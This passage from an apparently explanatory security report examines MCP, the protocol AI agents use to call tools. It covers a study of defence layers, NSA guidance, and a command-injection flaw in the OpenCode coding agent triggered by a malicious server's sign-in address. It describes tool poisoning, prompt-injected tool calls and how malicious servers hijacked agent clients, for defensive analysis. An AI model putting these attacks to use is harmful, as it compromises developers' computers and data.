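For each attack, the researchers identified the layer that could stop it earliest and another that could limit the damage. For example, a registry can reject a tool that is malicious when its developer submits it, but if the tool turns malicious later, the host application has to catch it. The researchers then judged which attacks each product could detect, block or limit, based on its design and not on tests.

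They conclude that existing defences concentrate on tools and leave gaps in the host application, the network connection and the supply chain. But their percentages are unreliable. The summary table lists ToolHive as covering 100% of registry attacks, while the detailed table lists it as covering none. According to the text, only one product protects the network connection, but the summary table shows three.

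In the detailed table, 11 of the 13 products address tool poisoning, and only one, MCP-Guard, addresses remote code execution in the host application. Yet Kraishan found no tool poisoning in the official registry, while many of the most serious flaws in real products let attackers run commands. Rostamzadeh and colleagues suggest that developers often put defences where tools are easiest to inspect, and a tool's description is easier to scan than its behaviour.

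The operating system isn't one of the six layers, so the study can't show how many of these attacks a sandbox would contain.

### What the NSA advises organisations to do

The NSA's information sheet from May 2026 is for organisations that use MCP in important systems. It says they can apply most of its advice with standard security software, without waiting for a change to the protocol. Its main recommendations are:

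- **Choose maintained servers** and review their code.
- **Separate sensitive data from public tools**, and send outgoing traffic through a proxy that permits only specified addresses.
- **Validate arguments** against the context in which the tool will use them, as well as against the schema.
- **Run each tool in a sandbox** and deny it any files or networks it doesn't need.
- **Sign messages** and give them an expiry time, so that nobody can alter or replay them.
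- **Treat every tool's output as untrusted** before passing it to another tool.
- **Log every call** with its exact arguments and the identity of the caller.
- **Track vulnerabilities**, keep an inventory of installed versions, and scan the network for open servers.

The documented flaws support the advice on sandboxes and proxies most strongly, because both still work when a developer has forgotten a check. Signatures would help less, because they would reveal a message altered on the network but not a harmful call caused by prompt injection, which the user's own client would sign.

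Network scans miss STDIO servers, so an organisation must look for them in configuration files on its employees' computers. Most of this work requires security staff, but someone working alone can choose maintained servers and give each one access to as few folders as possible.

### OpenCode: a fix without a warning

Tracking vulnerabilities works only if developers announce them. On 19 October 2026, Eilon Cohen of Pillar Security, which sells security for AI systems, disclosed a flaw in OpenCode, an open-source coding agent maintained by the company Anomaly. According to *Researchers Warn OpenCode Quietly Patched Critical RCE Flaw* (Poireault, 2026), Anomaly had fixed the flaw three weeks earlier without publishing an advisory or requesting a CVE number.

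The OpenCode flaw let a malicious remote MCP server run code on a developer's computer once the developer began to sign in, as The Hacker News' *OpenCode Flaw Lets Malicious MCP Servers Execute Code During Sign-In* (2026) explains. The server supplied the address of the sign-in page, and a library that OpenCode used to open the address passed it to PowerShell, which could then run part of it as a command. The flaw affected versions 1.0.137 to 1.18.32 on Windows, including the Windows Subsystem for Linux, which runs Linux programs.

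This is almost the same mistake as in mcp-remote, which JFrog disclosed 15 months earlier. In September 2025, Veria Labs' *From MCP to Shell* also showed that flaws in MCP sign-in let malicious servers take control of computers through Claude Code and Gemini CLI. The official guidance now tells clients never to open such addresses through a shell.

Pillar reported the OpenCode flaw at the end of August. A month later, Anomaly replied that malicious MCP servers were "outside their threat model", meaning it doesn't try to defend against them. That position is reasonable for local servers, but a remote server runs on someone else's computer, and connecting to it shouldn't let it run anything on the user's. Under MCP's security guidance, clients must prevent attacks that use malicious sign-in addresses.

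Anomaly nevertheless fixed the flaw on 28 September in version 1.18.33, which checks that a sign-in address begins in a permitted way. But Pillar's researchers showed that an ordinary `https` address could also carry the attack. They consider the library update more important because it correctly puts the address in quotation marks, so PowerShell no longer reads it as a command. Pillar rates the flaw at 9.8. Poireault doesn't mention any real attacks.

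Users of old versions remain exposed because this flaw has no published vulnerability record, and security scanners usually check installed software against such records. A company that updates its tools only after a security alert therefore has no reason to install 1.18.33, while attackers can read about the flaw in Pillar's report. An inventory of installed versions, which the NSA recommends, would let administrators find the affected computers once they learned of the flaw from the press.
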